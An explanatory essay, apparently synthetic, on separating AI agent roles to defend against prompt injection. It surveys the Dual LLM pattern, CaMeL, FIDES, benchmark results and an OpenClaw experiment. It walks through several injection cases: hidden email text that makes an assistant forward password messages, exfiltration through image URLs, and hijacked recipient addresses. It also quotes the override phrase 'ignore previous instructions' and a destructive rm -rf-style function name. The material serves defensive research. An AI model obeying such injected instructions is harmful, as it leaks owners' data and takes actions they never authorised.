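# Separating agent roles and mediating between them as a security architecture for AI systems

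## What is role separation for AI agents, and what is it meant to stop?

Role separation is a way of building AI systems so that the component that reads material from strangers does not also hold private data or the power to act. It applies to agents, which are language models run in a loop with tools (functions such as "search the mailbox" or "send a message") so that they can act as well as answer. It is meant to defend against prompt injection, in which an attacker places instructions in material an agent reads and the agent follows them.

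The simplest case is an email assistant, the example used in *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), a brief from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body. Suppose the owner asks the assistant to summarise the morning's mail. The assistant uses its reading tool to retrieve the text of every new message, including one from a stranger. That message contains instructions, perhaps in white type on a white background, to find messages about passwords and contracts and forward them to an outside address before writing the summary. The assistant calls the search tool, then the sending tool. The mail server confirms that the assistant's credentials are valid and delivers the mail, and the owner gets an ordinary-looking summary.

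The owner had allowed every tool call, and the attacker never guessed a password or exploited a bug in the mail server. The Forum calls this an indirect injection because the malicious text arrives in outside material, whereas in a direct injection the user types it.

The same brief analyses the case using what some practitioners call the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. The email assistant has all three. Removing any one of them stops this attack, so the owner could let the assistant read mail only from known senders, narrow the part of the inbox it can search, or restrict outgoing mail to approved addresses. But each restriction also removes something the owner wanted. Role separation aims to keep all three capabilities in the system as a whole without giving all three to any single agent. Whether this works depends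 on what passes between the agents, since two agents that exchange text freely are not much different from one agent with all three capabilities.

### Why the model obeys the letter

A language model works on one sequence of text. The software around it joins the developer's standing instructions, the owner's request and any tool results into that sequence, and the model computes its next words from all of it. Labels can mark where each part begins, but they are also input, and training only makes it likely that the model will respect them. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) describes the weakness as the lack of a formal way to distinguish instructions from data. *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, 2025) compares it to an old flaw of digital computers, which keep programs and data in the same memory, so that data can end up running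 as a program. The paper argues that the distinction is even less clear for agents, because the text an agent reads drives its planning.

Better labels would not solve the problem, because an agent often should act on what it reads. In one ordinary task from AgentDojo, a test suite described below, the agent has to pay the bill in a file named "bill-december-2023.txt", using the amount and payee given in the file. A filter that removed everything resembling an instruction would prevent the agent from completing the task, and a forged bill could contain nothing that looks like an attack.

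Developers train models to rank the developer's instructions above text from third parties, and this helps. But the Frontier Model Forum describes model-level failures as probabilistic and hard to predict, and recommends limits outside the agent's reasoning that no text in its context can override. Role separation is one such limit if ordinary code enforces the boundary between the agents.

### One layout with all the parts

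Suppose the owner now rebuilds the email assistant as several components. A customer's agent asks for a meeting next Tuesday, and the meeting requires a hotel room.

```
 customer's agent      strangers' email      hotel's agent
         \                    |                   /
          +------------ outer mediator ----------+
                              |
                        exposed agent
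                              |
                        inner mediator
                              |
                        trusted agent    (mailbox, calendar)
                              |
                           broker        (mail password, card)
                              |
                      mail server, bank
```

The *exposed agent* reads content or messages that an outsider can write. Here it reads incoming mail and deals with other firms' agents, and it holds nothing worth stealing. The *trusted agent* has access to the mailbox and the calendar. It is called trusted because of what it holds, not because it is reliable; it also runs on a language model, perhaps the same one. A *mediator* is any component that two agents' messages or requests must pass through and that can change or refuse them. In this layout, an outer mediator sits between the exposed agent and outsiders,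 and an inner one sits between the owner's two agents. The *broker* is a mediator that also holds credentials or authority and carries out approved actions itself. For example, the trusted agent can ask for a payment, but only the broker has the card. Each mediator sits on a *trust boundary*, where the system must check data or requests passing between two sides because it trusts them differently.

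In a given exchange, the *requester* is the party that asks for something and the *provider* is the party it asks. When the customer's agent asks for a meeting, it is the requester and the owner's exposed agent is the provider. The exposed agent then becomes a requester too when it asks the hotel's agent for a room for the meeting. An agent that is a provider to some parties and a requester to others is a *dual-role agent*. Agent-to-agent protocols, the message standards that agents of different owners use to call on each other, make such chains of requests easy to build.

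The exposed agent still receives the stranger's letter and may well obey it, but it has no mailbox to search for passwords. The attacker can now do harm only if the inner mediator lets through something that leads the trusted agent to propose a harmful action, and the broker approves that action.

Zhang and colleagues propose a similar design, AgentSandbox. A persistent agent keeps the user's long-term profile and never deals with outsiders, while a new temporary agent handles each task and is then discarded, along with any injected instructions. One filter limits the data the temporary agent receives, another checks what it returns, and a firewall with fixed rules screens its outside traffic. The Dual LLM pattern, an earlier proposal that splits one assistant between two models, uses only the middle of the diagram.

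### The older ideas behind the design

Most of this comes from computer security of the 1970s and 1980s. Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 tutorial, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, set out eight design principles that are still taught; Levchenko (2017), in *Principles*, reprints the page for a university security course. *Least privilege* means that every program and every user should operate with the smallest set of privileges the job requires, which limits the damage from an error. Denying the exposed agent a mailbox applies this principle directly. *Complete mediation* means that the system checks authority for every access to every object, with no path around the check. Saltzer and Schroeder concluded that a system should be wary of remembering the result of an earlier check, because authority may have changed since, and that it needs a foolproof way to identify the source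 of each request. An agent that has mixed the owner's words with a stranger's in one context has lost the information about which request came from whom.

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a program that could not keep its sources of authority apart. The program was a compiler at the computer company Tymshare. It collected usage statistics, and the operating system let it write to the system directory that held the statistics file. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user gave the name of the billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission to write there, and the debugging output replaced the company's billing records. The compiler had used its own permission on behalf of a user who had no right to change that file.

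A *confused deputy* is a program tricked into using its legitimate authority for someone who lacks that authority. Hardy rejects the obvious repairs. The compiler could refuse to write into the system directory, but some users had good reason to write there. It could refuse to write to the billing file by name, but other files were sensitive too, and the list of protected files would need updating whenever someone added another. His solution was the capability, an unforgeable token that both identifies a file and grants permission to use it. The user gives the compiler a capability for the debugging file, and the compiler uses only that one. A user who has no capability for the billing file cannot supply one. The email assistant in the opening case is a worse kind of confused deputy, because the stranger has no authority over it and still gets to use the owner's authority.

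The closest ancestor of the layout above is in OpenSSH, the widely used program for logging in to remote computers. Its server needs the highest privilege on the machine, but it must also process data from anyone who connects. *Preventing Privilege Escalation* (Provos, Friedl and Honeyman, 2003) splits the server into two processes. An unprivileged child process handles all the network traffic. A small privileged process, the monitor, holds the server's private key and checks passwords, and the child must send it a request for anything that needs privilege.

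The child may make only the requests listed in a short, predefined table, and the permitted requests change as the login proceeds. At the start, it may ask only for the key exchange parameters and a signature. It must then ask whether a user name is valid before it can submit a password or key for checking. If the child sends a request that isn't permitted at that point, the monitor shuts down. To get a signature, the child sends a hash to the monitor, which returns the signature, so the signing key never leaves the monitor.

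After the split, about 68% of the code, counting outside libraries, ran without privilege. Provos and colleagues make a back-of-the-envelope estimate that, if bugs are spread evenly, two thirds of them can no longer give an attacker control of the machine. Known flaws are better evidence. An integer overflow in the packet-handling code and a bug in a third-party compression library had each threatened to give remote attackers full control, and both were now in unprivileged code, where they could no longer do so. Login times barely changed. The remaining third of the code, together with the operating system that keeps the two processes apart, forms the *trusted computing base*, the components that must work correctly for the security claim to hold. Keeping it small matters because people have to audit it line by line.

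The analogy with OpenSSH weakens at the boundary between the agents. OpenSSH identifies each request type by a small number, which the monitor can check against a table. An exposed agent's most useful output is often a sentence, such as "the customer can do Tuesday, but only if the contract is ready", and no table lists the permissible sentences. The recipient is another language model, so a sentence that gets through can itself be an injection. OpenSSH's monitor may have a bug in the code that parses user names, but it doesn't interpret a user name as instructions. An attacker may not need a second injection. Debenedetti and colleagues give the example of a user who wants a hotel recommendation, where one hotel's listing contains text that makes the model always choose that hotel. An isolated reader would pass on the hotel's name in the correct form, but the attacker would still have determined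 the recommendation.

Provos and colleagues assume that the attacker has taken complete control of the child process, and then ask what the interface still allows. The same question applies unchanged to an exposed agent, and the answer does not depend on how often the agent resists injections.

### Who the attacker is

Designs of this kind mostly share a threat model, which Zhang and colleagues state explicitly. The attacker controls outside agents or tools, or the content they return, and wants either private data or a harmful action such as a payment. The user and the user's direct instructions are trusted. The defender controls the prompts, policies and added modules of the user's own agent, and how it communicates with outsiders. The underlying infrastructure, which includes the operating system, the broker's code and the company hosting the model, must also be trustworthy, because an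 attacker who controlled the broker could do harm without tricking the agent.

Role separation is not meant to stop jailbreaking, in which users try to make a model misbehave. It is also not meant to stop an agent from misunderstanding a harmless request and deleting the wrong files, though the Frontier Model Forum notes that the same limits may contain that damage. Denial of service is usually out of scope too, because an attacker who can write to the exposed agent can probably stop it from working.

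### How to measure a defence

Research in this field often reports two numbers. *Benign utility* is the share of ordinary tasks a system completes when nobody attacks it. *Attack success rate* is the share of attacks in a test that achieve the attacker's goal. Neither means much alone, because an agent that refuses every request has an attack success rate of zero but completes no tasks.

Researchers usually measure both with AgentDojo, a benchmark built by Debenedetti and colleagues. It simulates four applications with working tools: an office workspace with email, a Slack team chat, a travel agency and a bank. It has 97 user tasks and 27 attacker goals. Within each application, the benchmark pairs every task with every goal (40 × 6 for the workspace, 21 × 5 for Slack, 20 × 7 for travel, 16 × 9 for the bank), for 629 security cases in total. For each case, it plants the attack text somewhere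 an outsider could plausibly have written it, runs the agent, and then uses ordinary code to check the result, such as whether the money moved or the email went out. A language model would be a poor judge here because the injection might fool it as well.

The first results included a crude form of role separation called a *tool filter*, in which the model chose the tools it needed before it saw any untrusted data. A model asked to summarise email, for example, then had no means of sending any. On GPT-4o, OpenAI's leading model at the time, this cut the attack success rate to 7.5%, from about 48% for a well-addressed injection against the undefended model. The filter cannot help when the tools needed for the task are also enough for the attack, as they were in 17% of cases. The model scores are now out of date, but they show that a low attack success rate can simply mean the agent is incompetent.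 The more capable models tended to be easier to attack, because the weaker ones often bungled the attacker's task even after the injection had worked.

AgentDojo remains in wide use. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports that it has over 900 pairs of tasks and attacks, and *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) used it to test 13 models from six providers. *StepGuard* (2026) uses both AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a newer benchmark with longer tasks in which some third-party instructions are helpful and the agent should follow them. This makes AgentDyn harder for a defence that works by ignoring third-party instructions. A larger gap is in testing attacks that lie dormant in an agent's memory. Chu (2026), in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, reviewed 116 papers and found no benchmark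 that tests attacks carried from one session to the next, though a single author did all the classifying.

An attack success rate depends heavily on who did the attacking. A *fixed attack set* is a list of injections written in advance, usually without the defence in mind. An *adaptive attacker* knows how the defence works and revises each attempt based on the result, using as much computing time as it takes. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) used adaptive attacks against 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although the original papers had reported rates near zero for the majority.

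Two of the twelve defences, spotlighting and prompt sandwiching, did far worse against adaptive attacks than against stock ones. Spotlighting uses special markers to set trusted text apart from untrusted text, and prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. Nasr and colleagues measured attack success rates as low as 1% with AgentDojo's stock attacks. Their automated search, which kept rewriting the injections, raised the rate above 95% for both defences. One successful injection posed as an access-policy notice and presented the attacker's steps as prerequisites for the user's own task, starting with inviting an outsider to the Slack workspace. Repeating the user's request doesn't help against this injection, because the attacker's steps appear to be part of fulfilling it. Human attackers in a competition with over 500 participants also beat the two defences, hundreds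 of times in total. Each of the 12 defences had its own test, so the figures can't be used to rank them.

Both of those defences leave a single model with the untrusted text and the tools, and try to make it read more carefully. Role separation is meant to prevent harm even when the agent exposed to that text is fooled. If ordinary code enforces the boundary, as with OpenSSH's table of requests, one can check whether it does so by reading the code. But if the mediator is a language model that judges free text, security again depends on how well a model reads, and a low attack success rate for stock injections is weak evidence that the mediator will resist an attacker who has studied it.

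## How can one assistant be split into a part that reads and a part that acts?

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting the assistant into two language models with an ordinary program between them. Willison, a software developer who had named prompt injection the year before, wanted an assistant that could use his private data and tools without obeying everyone who wrote to him. His *privileged model* takes the owner's requests, plans the work and calls tools. His *quarantined model* reads anything a stranger may have written. It has no tools, and Willison assumes it may misbehave at any moment. The program, called the *controller*, runs the tools and carries everything that passes between the models. In the layout above, the privileged model would be the trusted agent and the quarantined model the exposed agent. The controller would be both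 the inner mediator and the broker, although it carries out whatever the privileged model asks without checking the request.

The quarantined model's text must never reach the privileged model unfiltered, because it may carry the stranger's injection with it. So the controller stores each piece of outside text under a name, such as `$VAR1`, and gives the privileged model only the name. Willison's own example is a request to summarise the latest email:

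| Step | Privileged model sees | Controller does | Quarantined model sees |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | The owner's request | Fetches the email that the privileged model asks for and stores the text as `$VAR1` | Nothing |
| 2 | The name `$VAR1` | Receives the order to summarise `$VAR1`, replaces the name with the email's text, and passes it on | The order to summarise and the whole email |
| 3 | A notice that the summary is ready | Stores the summary as `$VAR2` | Nothing more |
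| 4 | The name `$VAR2` | Receives the order to display `$VAR2`, replaces the name with the summary, and shows it to the owner | Nothing more |

If the email contains instructions to find and forward messages about passwords, the quarantined model may well follow them. But a model calls a tool by writing a command in an agreed format, which the surrounding program finds and executes, and here the controller looks for commands only in the privileged model's output. If the quarantined model writes a valid command to search the mailbox, the controller stores it in `$VAR2` as part of the summary. The owner gets a strange summary, but the controller doesn't forward any messages, even if neither model recognises the attack.

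Willison allows one exception to the rule. If the quarantined model only has to sort a text into one of a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the answer exactly matches one of them and then pass it to the privileged model. This lets the assistant handle a meeting request differently from an invoice. Otherwise, the privileged model has to plan without any information about the email's contents.

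That is a serious restriction. Willison's first example is a request to update his to-do list with the action items from a colleague's latest email. The pattern can handle this, because the quarantined model extracts the items and the privileged model adds `$VAR2` to the list without seeing what it contains. But if one item is to book a room for Thursday, the assistant can't book it, because the model with the booking tool can't read the item. The to-do list also now contains text from an outsider. If the privileged model reads the list next week, it will be exposed to any injection in that text, so the controller has to keep treating those entries as untrusted. Willison warns about such chains, in which one model's output becomes another's input.

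He called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes the assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and one programming mistake that lets outside text through to the privileged model wastes all the effort. He proposed it anyway because the usual alternative was to ask the owner to approve every action, and he expected owners to learn to click "OK" as fast as possible.

### What the attacker still controls

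The privileged model cannot check a value it never reads. Suppose the owner asks the assistant to send a contract to the accountant, whose address is in an email thread that a stranger has joined. The quarantined model looks for the address, the controller stores the result as `$VAR1`, and the privileged model calls the sending tool with `$VAR1` as the recipient. An instruction hidden in the thread can make the quarantined model return the stranger's address instead. The privileged model still makes the tool call it planned, but the contract goes to the stranger. AgentDojo's bill-paying task has the same problem, because the assistant can pay a forged bill without the privileged model ever reading it.

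*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) distinguishes control flow (which tools run and in what order) from data flow (the values they receive). Willison's Dual LLM pattern takes control flow away from the attacker. Protecting data flow requires labels that record where each value came from and a check on those labels before a sensitive call. CaMeL, a later system built on the Dual LLM pattern, adds both.

Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, established the same limit with a proof assistant, a program that checks every step of a mathematical proof. The method compares an agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The agent counts as secure if it reveals nothing to an attacker that the reference agent wouldn't. In one example, the plan reads Alice's private notes and an attacker's email, gives both to the quarantined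 model to write a reply, and sends it. The reference agent's reply depends only on the email. When the quarantined model obeys an injection, it quotes the notes in the reply, and the plan sends them to the attacker. Dongol concludes that the split stops injected tool calls but not injected content in a value that the plan uses.

The result covers only that plan and doesn't show that every Dual LLM assistant leaks. The leak happens only when a quarantined model sees a secret and the attacker's text together, and an output goes back to the attacker. A designer can prevent the first condition by keeping the notes out of the prompt. But then the reply can't draw on them, and people often want an assistant to answer a stranger's question from their own files.

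Displaying the quarantined model's output to the owner can also leak private data. If the model has seen such data, it can write a summary containing an image whose web address encodes it, and displaying the image sends the data to the attacker's server. Willison therefore forbids such a model to produce outbound links or images. The owner could still be persuaded to send the data. In his example, a summary contains a block of scrambled text and tells the reader to paste it into a certain website to see a funny picture of a monkey. An attacker can also reach the privileged model through the owner, because that model treats whatever the owner types as trusted, including text copied from a malicious page.

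### Giving up the general-purpose agent

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) include Willison's proposal as one of six patterns for building agents. They think general-purpose agents are unlikely to give "meaningful and reliable safety guarantees" while both the agents and their defences rely on the current class of language models. They expect better training and attack detectors to help but to remain heuristic. They point to computer vision, where over a decade of research on images altered to fool classifiers has produced no general solution.

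This is a judgement about where research is going, not a proof, but test results for strong models fit it. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) quote Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, which Anthropic has since superseded. In coding environments, attackers who adapted their injections succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. A failure rate of a few percent may be tolerable when failures are accidental, but it is much less reassuring when an attacker can keep trying.

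Beurer-Kellner and colleagues therefore ask what useful work an agent can still do if it isn't expected to do everything. All six patterns follow the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects. The agent's output must also not cause harm later, for example by leaking private data through a link.

A designer can apply part of this principle with a single agent by removing its dangerous tools as soon as it reads something untrusted. Dongol calls this a *fence* and proves that it works for agents whose plan is fixed beforehand, provided that each injection amounts to a single tool call, the fence covers every tool an injection could call, and the agent never gets those tools back. But if the fence removes the sending tool, the agent can't reply to an email it has read. Dividing the roles keeps that tool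 available in a different agent.

Three of the six patterns divide the work in this way. One is the Dual LLM pattern itself. Another, *map-reduce*, is a simpler version that gives each document its own isolated model. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of an assistant that must find this month's invoices and email them to the accounts department. An isolated model reads each file and may answer only yes or no to whether it is an invoice. Another model then writes the email and sends the files marked yes. An attacker can get a malicious file marked as an invoice, but could have done the same by writing a real invoice. The malicious file can't affect how the assistant treats any other file. This holds only if the sending model attaches the files without reading them, since reading them would expose it to the injection.

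In the *code-then-execute* pattern, the privileged model writes a complete program before any model reads untrusted data. The program calls the tools and passes any text that needs processing to models without tools. For a request to send today's schedule to the boss, the program would read the calendar, have a model format the entries, and email the result to a fixed address. An injection in a calendar entry can change the body of the email but not the recipient, because the address is part of the program.

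The other three patterns restrict a single agent. The *action-selector* chooses from a menu of fixed actions and never sees their results. *Plan-then-execute* commits the agent to a list of tool calls before it reads anything. *Context minimisation* removes the user's words before the agent writes its answer, so a customer who asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote can't also talk it into a discount.

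A case study of an assistant that sorts files on a computer shows why dividing the roles can be safer than planning alone. Even if a plan contains only commands to find and move files, an injection that controls what the commands apply to can make the assistant find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. If a separate, isolated model handles each file and can only choose from a list of categories, a malicious file can influence only where it is moved itself. Some tasks can't be divided this way because deciding about one file requires reading another.

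Beurer-Kellner and colleagues find that the split gives less protection in their case study of an email and calendar assistant. The quarantined model drafts replies as free text, which the privileged model never reads but the recipient does. An injection can make the draft pass instructions to the owner's colleagues, or carry private data in non-printing characters that the owner can't see even when checking the draft. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect the split to make such an assistant only slightly less useful, because it shouldn't take new instructions from untrusted data anyway.

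Designers must partly guess how strict a format has to be before text can safely reach the acting agent. For a programming assistant, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a quarantined model could turn untrusted documentation into a bare description of the available functions, with names of at most 30 characters. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, a commentary on the paper of the same name, wonders whether even that is safe. His example is the 29-character name `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which spells out a command for deleting files.

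### A reader and an actor in OpenClaw

In *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw*, Cheng and Tsao (2026), of the security company Trend Micro, measured how much of the protection comes from dividing the tools and how much from restricting the format. They used OpenClaw, an open-source platform for agents with many tools, and took their attacks from LLMail-Inject, a public challenge run by Microsoft. Contestants wrote emails that tried to make an assistant send an unauthorised message when it was asked to summarise the mailbox or answer a question about it.

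The challenge had collected 461,640 submissions. Cheng and Tsao took the successful ones from its first phase and removed duplicates, which left 22,899. They ran these against a single agent using OpenAI's gpt-5-mini, with no added defence. Of these attacks, 649 (2.83%) succeeded, and they became the test set for all their later tests.

The defended version has two agents that share no tools, an arrangement known as *tool partitioning*. The *reader* sees the raw emails and has one tool, which stores a summary. The *actor* never sees the emails. Its tools fetch the reader's summary, store a result and send mail. In the full version, the reader must also write its summary in JSON, a standard format for labelled data, with fields for the sender, subject, body summary and any action items. A short program then searches the summary for email addresses, fragments of tool calls and common injection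 phrases such as "ignore previous instructions". During the experiment, this program only recorded what it found and let every summary through.

Cheng and Tsao also tested each half of the defence alone. One configuration had two agents that passed ordinary prose, and the other had a single agent that used the JSON format but kept all its tools. The numbers of successful attacks were:

| Scenario | Attacks | JSON format alone | Two agents alone | Both |
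|---|---|---|---|---|
| Summarise 2 emails | 149 | 6 | 1 | 0 |
| Summarise 10 emails | 211 | 30 | 1 | 0 |
| Answer a question using retrieved emails | 116 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| The same, with budget figures as the target | 173 | 49 | 0 | 0 |
| All | 649 | 92 (14.18%) | 2 (0.31%) | 0 (0%) |

Dividing the tools accounted for nearly all of the reduction in successful attacks. The format alone was least effective when the attacker wanted budget figures. In that case, 28.3% of attacks still succeeded because the agent that filled in the form could also send the mail.

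### What zero out of 649 can show

Tool partitioning guarantees that the reader cannot send mail, as long as OpenClaw's own code works as intended. OpenClaw doesn't give the reader the tool for sending mail, and nothing written in an email can change that. The contestants had written their attacks to make the agent that reads mail also send mail. Such attacks always fail against the split system, however convincing they are.

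But the partition does not rule out unauthorised mail, because the actor can send mail and reads a summary written by a model that an attacker may control. Cheng and Tsao overstate the protection when they write that isolation blocks data theft "categorically". The summary can mislead the actor, and whether it does depends on the actor's model, as it did with a single agent. In the two attacks that succeeded against the version without JSON, the actor sent the mail after reading only what the reader had passed on.

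The full design also breaks Willison's rule that the privileged model never receives the quarantined model's free text, because the actor reads the body summary and the action items, which are both free text inside a labelled field. Cheng and Tsao report that injected content reached 63.7% of the reader's summaries in the full version. That figure seems to come from the pattern-matching program, so it may include summaries that only repeated a suspicious address and miss injections that the reader paraphrased. Even so, the format did not keep the attacker's material from the actor. Cheng and Tsao's explanation is that the material arrived without the persuasive framing that had made it work.

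An attacker who knew about the second agent could write text aimed at it. The "action items" field looks especially useful for this, because the second agent reads it to learn what needs doing. An email that politely asks for the budget figures to be sent to a new auditor contains no trick phrases, and a reading agent that summarised it accurately would list the request as an action item. If the checking program blocked summaries instead of just recording them, it would catch an address written out in full, but it would also block every legitimate summary that contained one. Cheng and Tsao say they did not test attacks designed to survive the summary and the handover. The defences that Nasr and colleagues broke had looked just as good against attacks that weren't designed to beat them.

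Even for old attacks, the true success rate could be above zero. If each attack had an independent chance *p* of succeeding, the chance of seeing no successes in 649 attempts would be (1 − *p*)^649. That falls to 5% when *p* is about 0.46%, so the data are compatible with any rate up to roughly one in 217, at 95% confidence. This bound applies only to attacks drawn from the same pool, and it is probably slightly too low because one contestant may have written many similar emails. The difference between two successes and none could also be due to chance. The experiment therefore gives good evidence for separating the tools, but hardly any that the JSON format helps once they are separate.

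The single agent has a 100% attack success rate because Cheng and Tsao chose 649 attacks that had each succeeded against it. Language models' outputs vary from run to run, so some of these attacks would probably fail if repeated against the same agent, and the paper doesn't report a second run. This variation could account for part of the improvement from the JSON format, but it is unlikely to account for a drop from 649 successful attacks to 2.

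The largest omission is benign utility, because Cheng and Tsao do not report how many ordinary tasks either version completed. The choice of tasks makes this worse. Summarising a mailbox or answering a question about it doesn't require sending mail, so an actor that never used its sending tool could still complete these tasks. The experiment includes no task like replying to an email, where the actor has to send something and its content has to depend on what the reader wrote.

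### Later tests

As of October 2026, no independent group appears to have repeated the OpenClaw experiment or attacked its design with adaptive injections. Narisetty and colleagues, who work for the security vendor LaunchSafe, compared seven systems that enforce security outside the model and found that each had been tested mainly on attacks fixed in advance. They list the overhead of the Dual LLM pattern as "design only", because Willison published a design without measurements. They ran their own adaptive test, which has not been peer-reviewed, on Progent, a system that checks each tool call against a set of rules. The adaptive attack did no better than the standard one. But they used a single hand-written attack template and a small model, and Progent does not separate reading from acting, so the result is weak evidence about what happens when an attacker uses a compromised reader against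 the actor.

In *ORBIT*, Hagag, Anderson and colleagues (2026) tested a version of the Dual LLM pattern as one of four defences for teams of agents. Their quarantined model summarises tool output to clean it. On programming tasks in which several agents fix problems in the same code, this lowered the share of problems solved by 9.2 percentage points when nobody was attacking (95% interval 4.5 to 14.0). None of the other three defences detectably lowered the share solved on those tasks. Summaries leave out details that a programmer often needs, such as the exact error message.

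The experiments reported in *ORBIT* covered harmful requests from users, an agent that already works for the attacker, and agents that collude. They did not include prompt injection, so they do not settle how well the split resists it. With one compromised agent in the team, the Dual LLM version lowered attack success from 72% to 48%, a change that Hagag and colleagues do not mark as statistically significant. A second model that checked each action lowered it to 12%. A quarantined model can clean what an agent reads, but this helps little when the agent is already hostile. Hagag and colleagues also used fixed attack templates, which they say probably makes the defences look better than they are.

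## What may safely pass from the exposed agent to the trusted one?

After a split, an attacker may no longer be able to choose which tools the assistant calls, but may still choose the values it passes to them. *PlanGuard* (2026), a proposal for checking an agent's actions against a plan, distinguishes *function hijacking*, in which an injection makes the agent call a tool the user never asked for, from *argument hijacking*, in which the agent calls the right tool with the wrong values. For example, the agent might delete a system directory when the user asked it to delete a temporary folder.

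*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025), the Google DeepMind paper that introduced CaMeL, gives a worked example. The owner asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and says that the meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name. The *control flow* is the sequence of steps: find the notes, extract the name and address, fetch the document, and send it. The *data flow* takes the document's name from the notes to the fetching tool, and Bob's address to the sending tool.

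An attacker who has edited the notes can redirect the document without changing any of these steps, as with the accountant's contract in the Dual LLM pattern. The attacker can also replace the document's name so that the assistant sends a different file. Willison (2025) wrote in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that this flaw in his Dual LLM pattern was new to him.

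*The LLMbda Calculus* reports that in 97 of AgentDojo's 144 banking cases, the attack needs a tool call or file that a program written for the user's task would never include, so fixing the plan in advance is generally enough to stop the attack. In the other 47, the legitimate plan already contains everything the attacker needs.

### CaMeL: a program with a check before each call

CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", keeps Willison's two models and adds a check on the data flow. The privileged model sees the owner's request and the descriptions of the tools, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. For Bob's document, a simplified version might be:

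```
notes    = find_file("notes of last meeting")
name     = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_file(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary code, replaces Willison's controller and runs the program. When the program needs to extract something from a text, the quarantined model must return a value of the requested type, such as an email address, and the interpreter stores it in a variable.

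The interpreter also attaches a *capability* to each value. This capability is more like a tag than like Hardy's token. *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes it as recording the value's sources and who may read it. Derived values inherit these tags, so the interpreter treats `address`, which comes from `notes`, as possibly written by anyone who could edit the notes. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs that tool's policy, a short Python function that examines the arguments and their tags and can allow the call, refuse it or ask the owner.

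Suppose the policy for sending mail requires every recipient to be a permitted reader of the attachment. This blocks an injection that replaces Bob's address with a stranger's, because the stranger isn't permitted to read the document. It also blocks an injection that substitutes the salary list, if Bob isn't permitted to read that. But the attacker can substitute an outdated version of the contract that Bob is permitted to read. The policy doesn't block this because it checks only permissions, and the only record of which document Bob wanted is in the notes that the attacker edited.

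Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues wrote that CaMeL "effectively solves the AgentDojo benchmark". According to *The LLMbda Calculus*, two injections were scored as successful in their tests. One hijacked a task in which the user tells the assistant to make a payment described in a document, a case that the CaMeL paper places outside its threat model. In the other, the assistant quoted hotel reviews word for word, and AgentDojo wrongly counted the quotation as a successful attack.

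In later tests, CaMeL completed far fewer tasks with its policies on. *The LLMbda Calculus* reports a rerun of CaMeL on the banking tasks, three times each. With the policy checks on, it completed 18 of 48 runs (37.5%) with each of two models, about half as many as with the checks off. Some injections succeeded without the checks and none with them, although not all the attacked runs finished. The developers of TypeGuard, a comparable system, found a similar drop on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, where CaMeL completed 7 of 21 with policies on and TypeGuard completed 8. They concluded that many of these tasks require data flows "no secure policy would admit". A test of CaMeL with its policies off is therefore weak evidence of how useful it is when it protects data flow.

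Someone also has to write and maintain the policies, a limitation the CaMeL paper acknowledges. Policies that often ask for approval bring back the habit of clicking "OK" that Willison wanted to avoid. He is nervous about any design that makes users think about security policies, noting that after two decades of involvement in application security he still hasn't fully worked out Amazon's cloud permissions system. *CaMeLoT* proposes checking the generated program against rules before it runs, in addition to the checks at each call.

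### How labels spread in FIDES

FIDES, a system from Microsoft, also tracks where data came from, but its planner chooses one tool call at a time instead of writing the whole program in advance. It gives each piece of data an *integrity* label, which records who could have written it, and a *confidentiality* label, which records who is allowed to read it (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025, *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*). When a program or model combines two pieces of data, anyone who could have written either one could have influenced the result, so the result's integrity label includes all of them. Its confidentiality label includes only those allowed to read both pieces.

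For example, an assistant might draft a reply to a stranger using the owner's private notes:

| Data | Possible writers | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| Private notes | Owner | Owner, Bob |
| Stranger's email | Stranger | Owner, stranger |
| Reply drafted from both | Owner, stranger | Owner |

The assistant may not send this reply to the stranger, which prevents the leak in Dongol's example even if the quarantined model has obeyed an injection and quoted the notes. But this also blocks a harmless reply that used nothing from the notes, because FIDES cannot determine which parts of a model's input influenced its output and so treats the output as influenced by all of them.

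The simplest integrity labels are "trusted" and "untrusted", and anything derived even partly from untrusted data is untrusted. An ordinary agent's next action depends on its whole conversation so far, so once it has read a web page, every later tool call is untrusted. FIDES avoids this by storing a tool result in a variable whenever showing it to the planner would change the conversation's label. Trusted results stay visible, so the planner has more information than Willison's privileged model.

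Before each sensitive call, a policy engine checks the labels. A strict policy for payments requires that the planner chose the tool in a trusted conversation and that every argument is trusted. A looser policy for messages requires a trusted recipient but allows an untrusted body, since people often want to forward or summarise what a stranger wrote. If an untrusted value reaches an argument that must be trusted, FIDES blocks the call and notifies the planner, which can then try something else.

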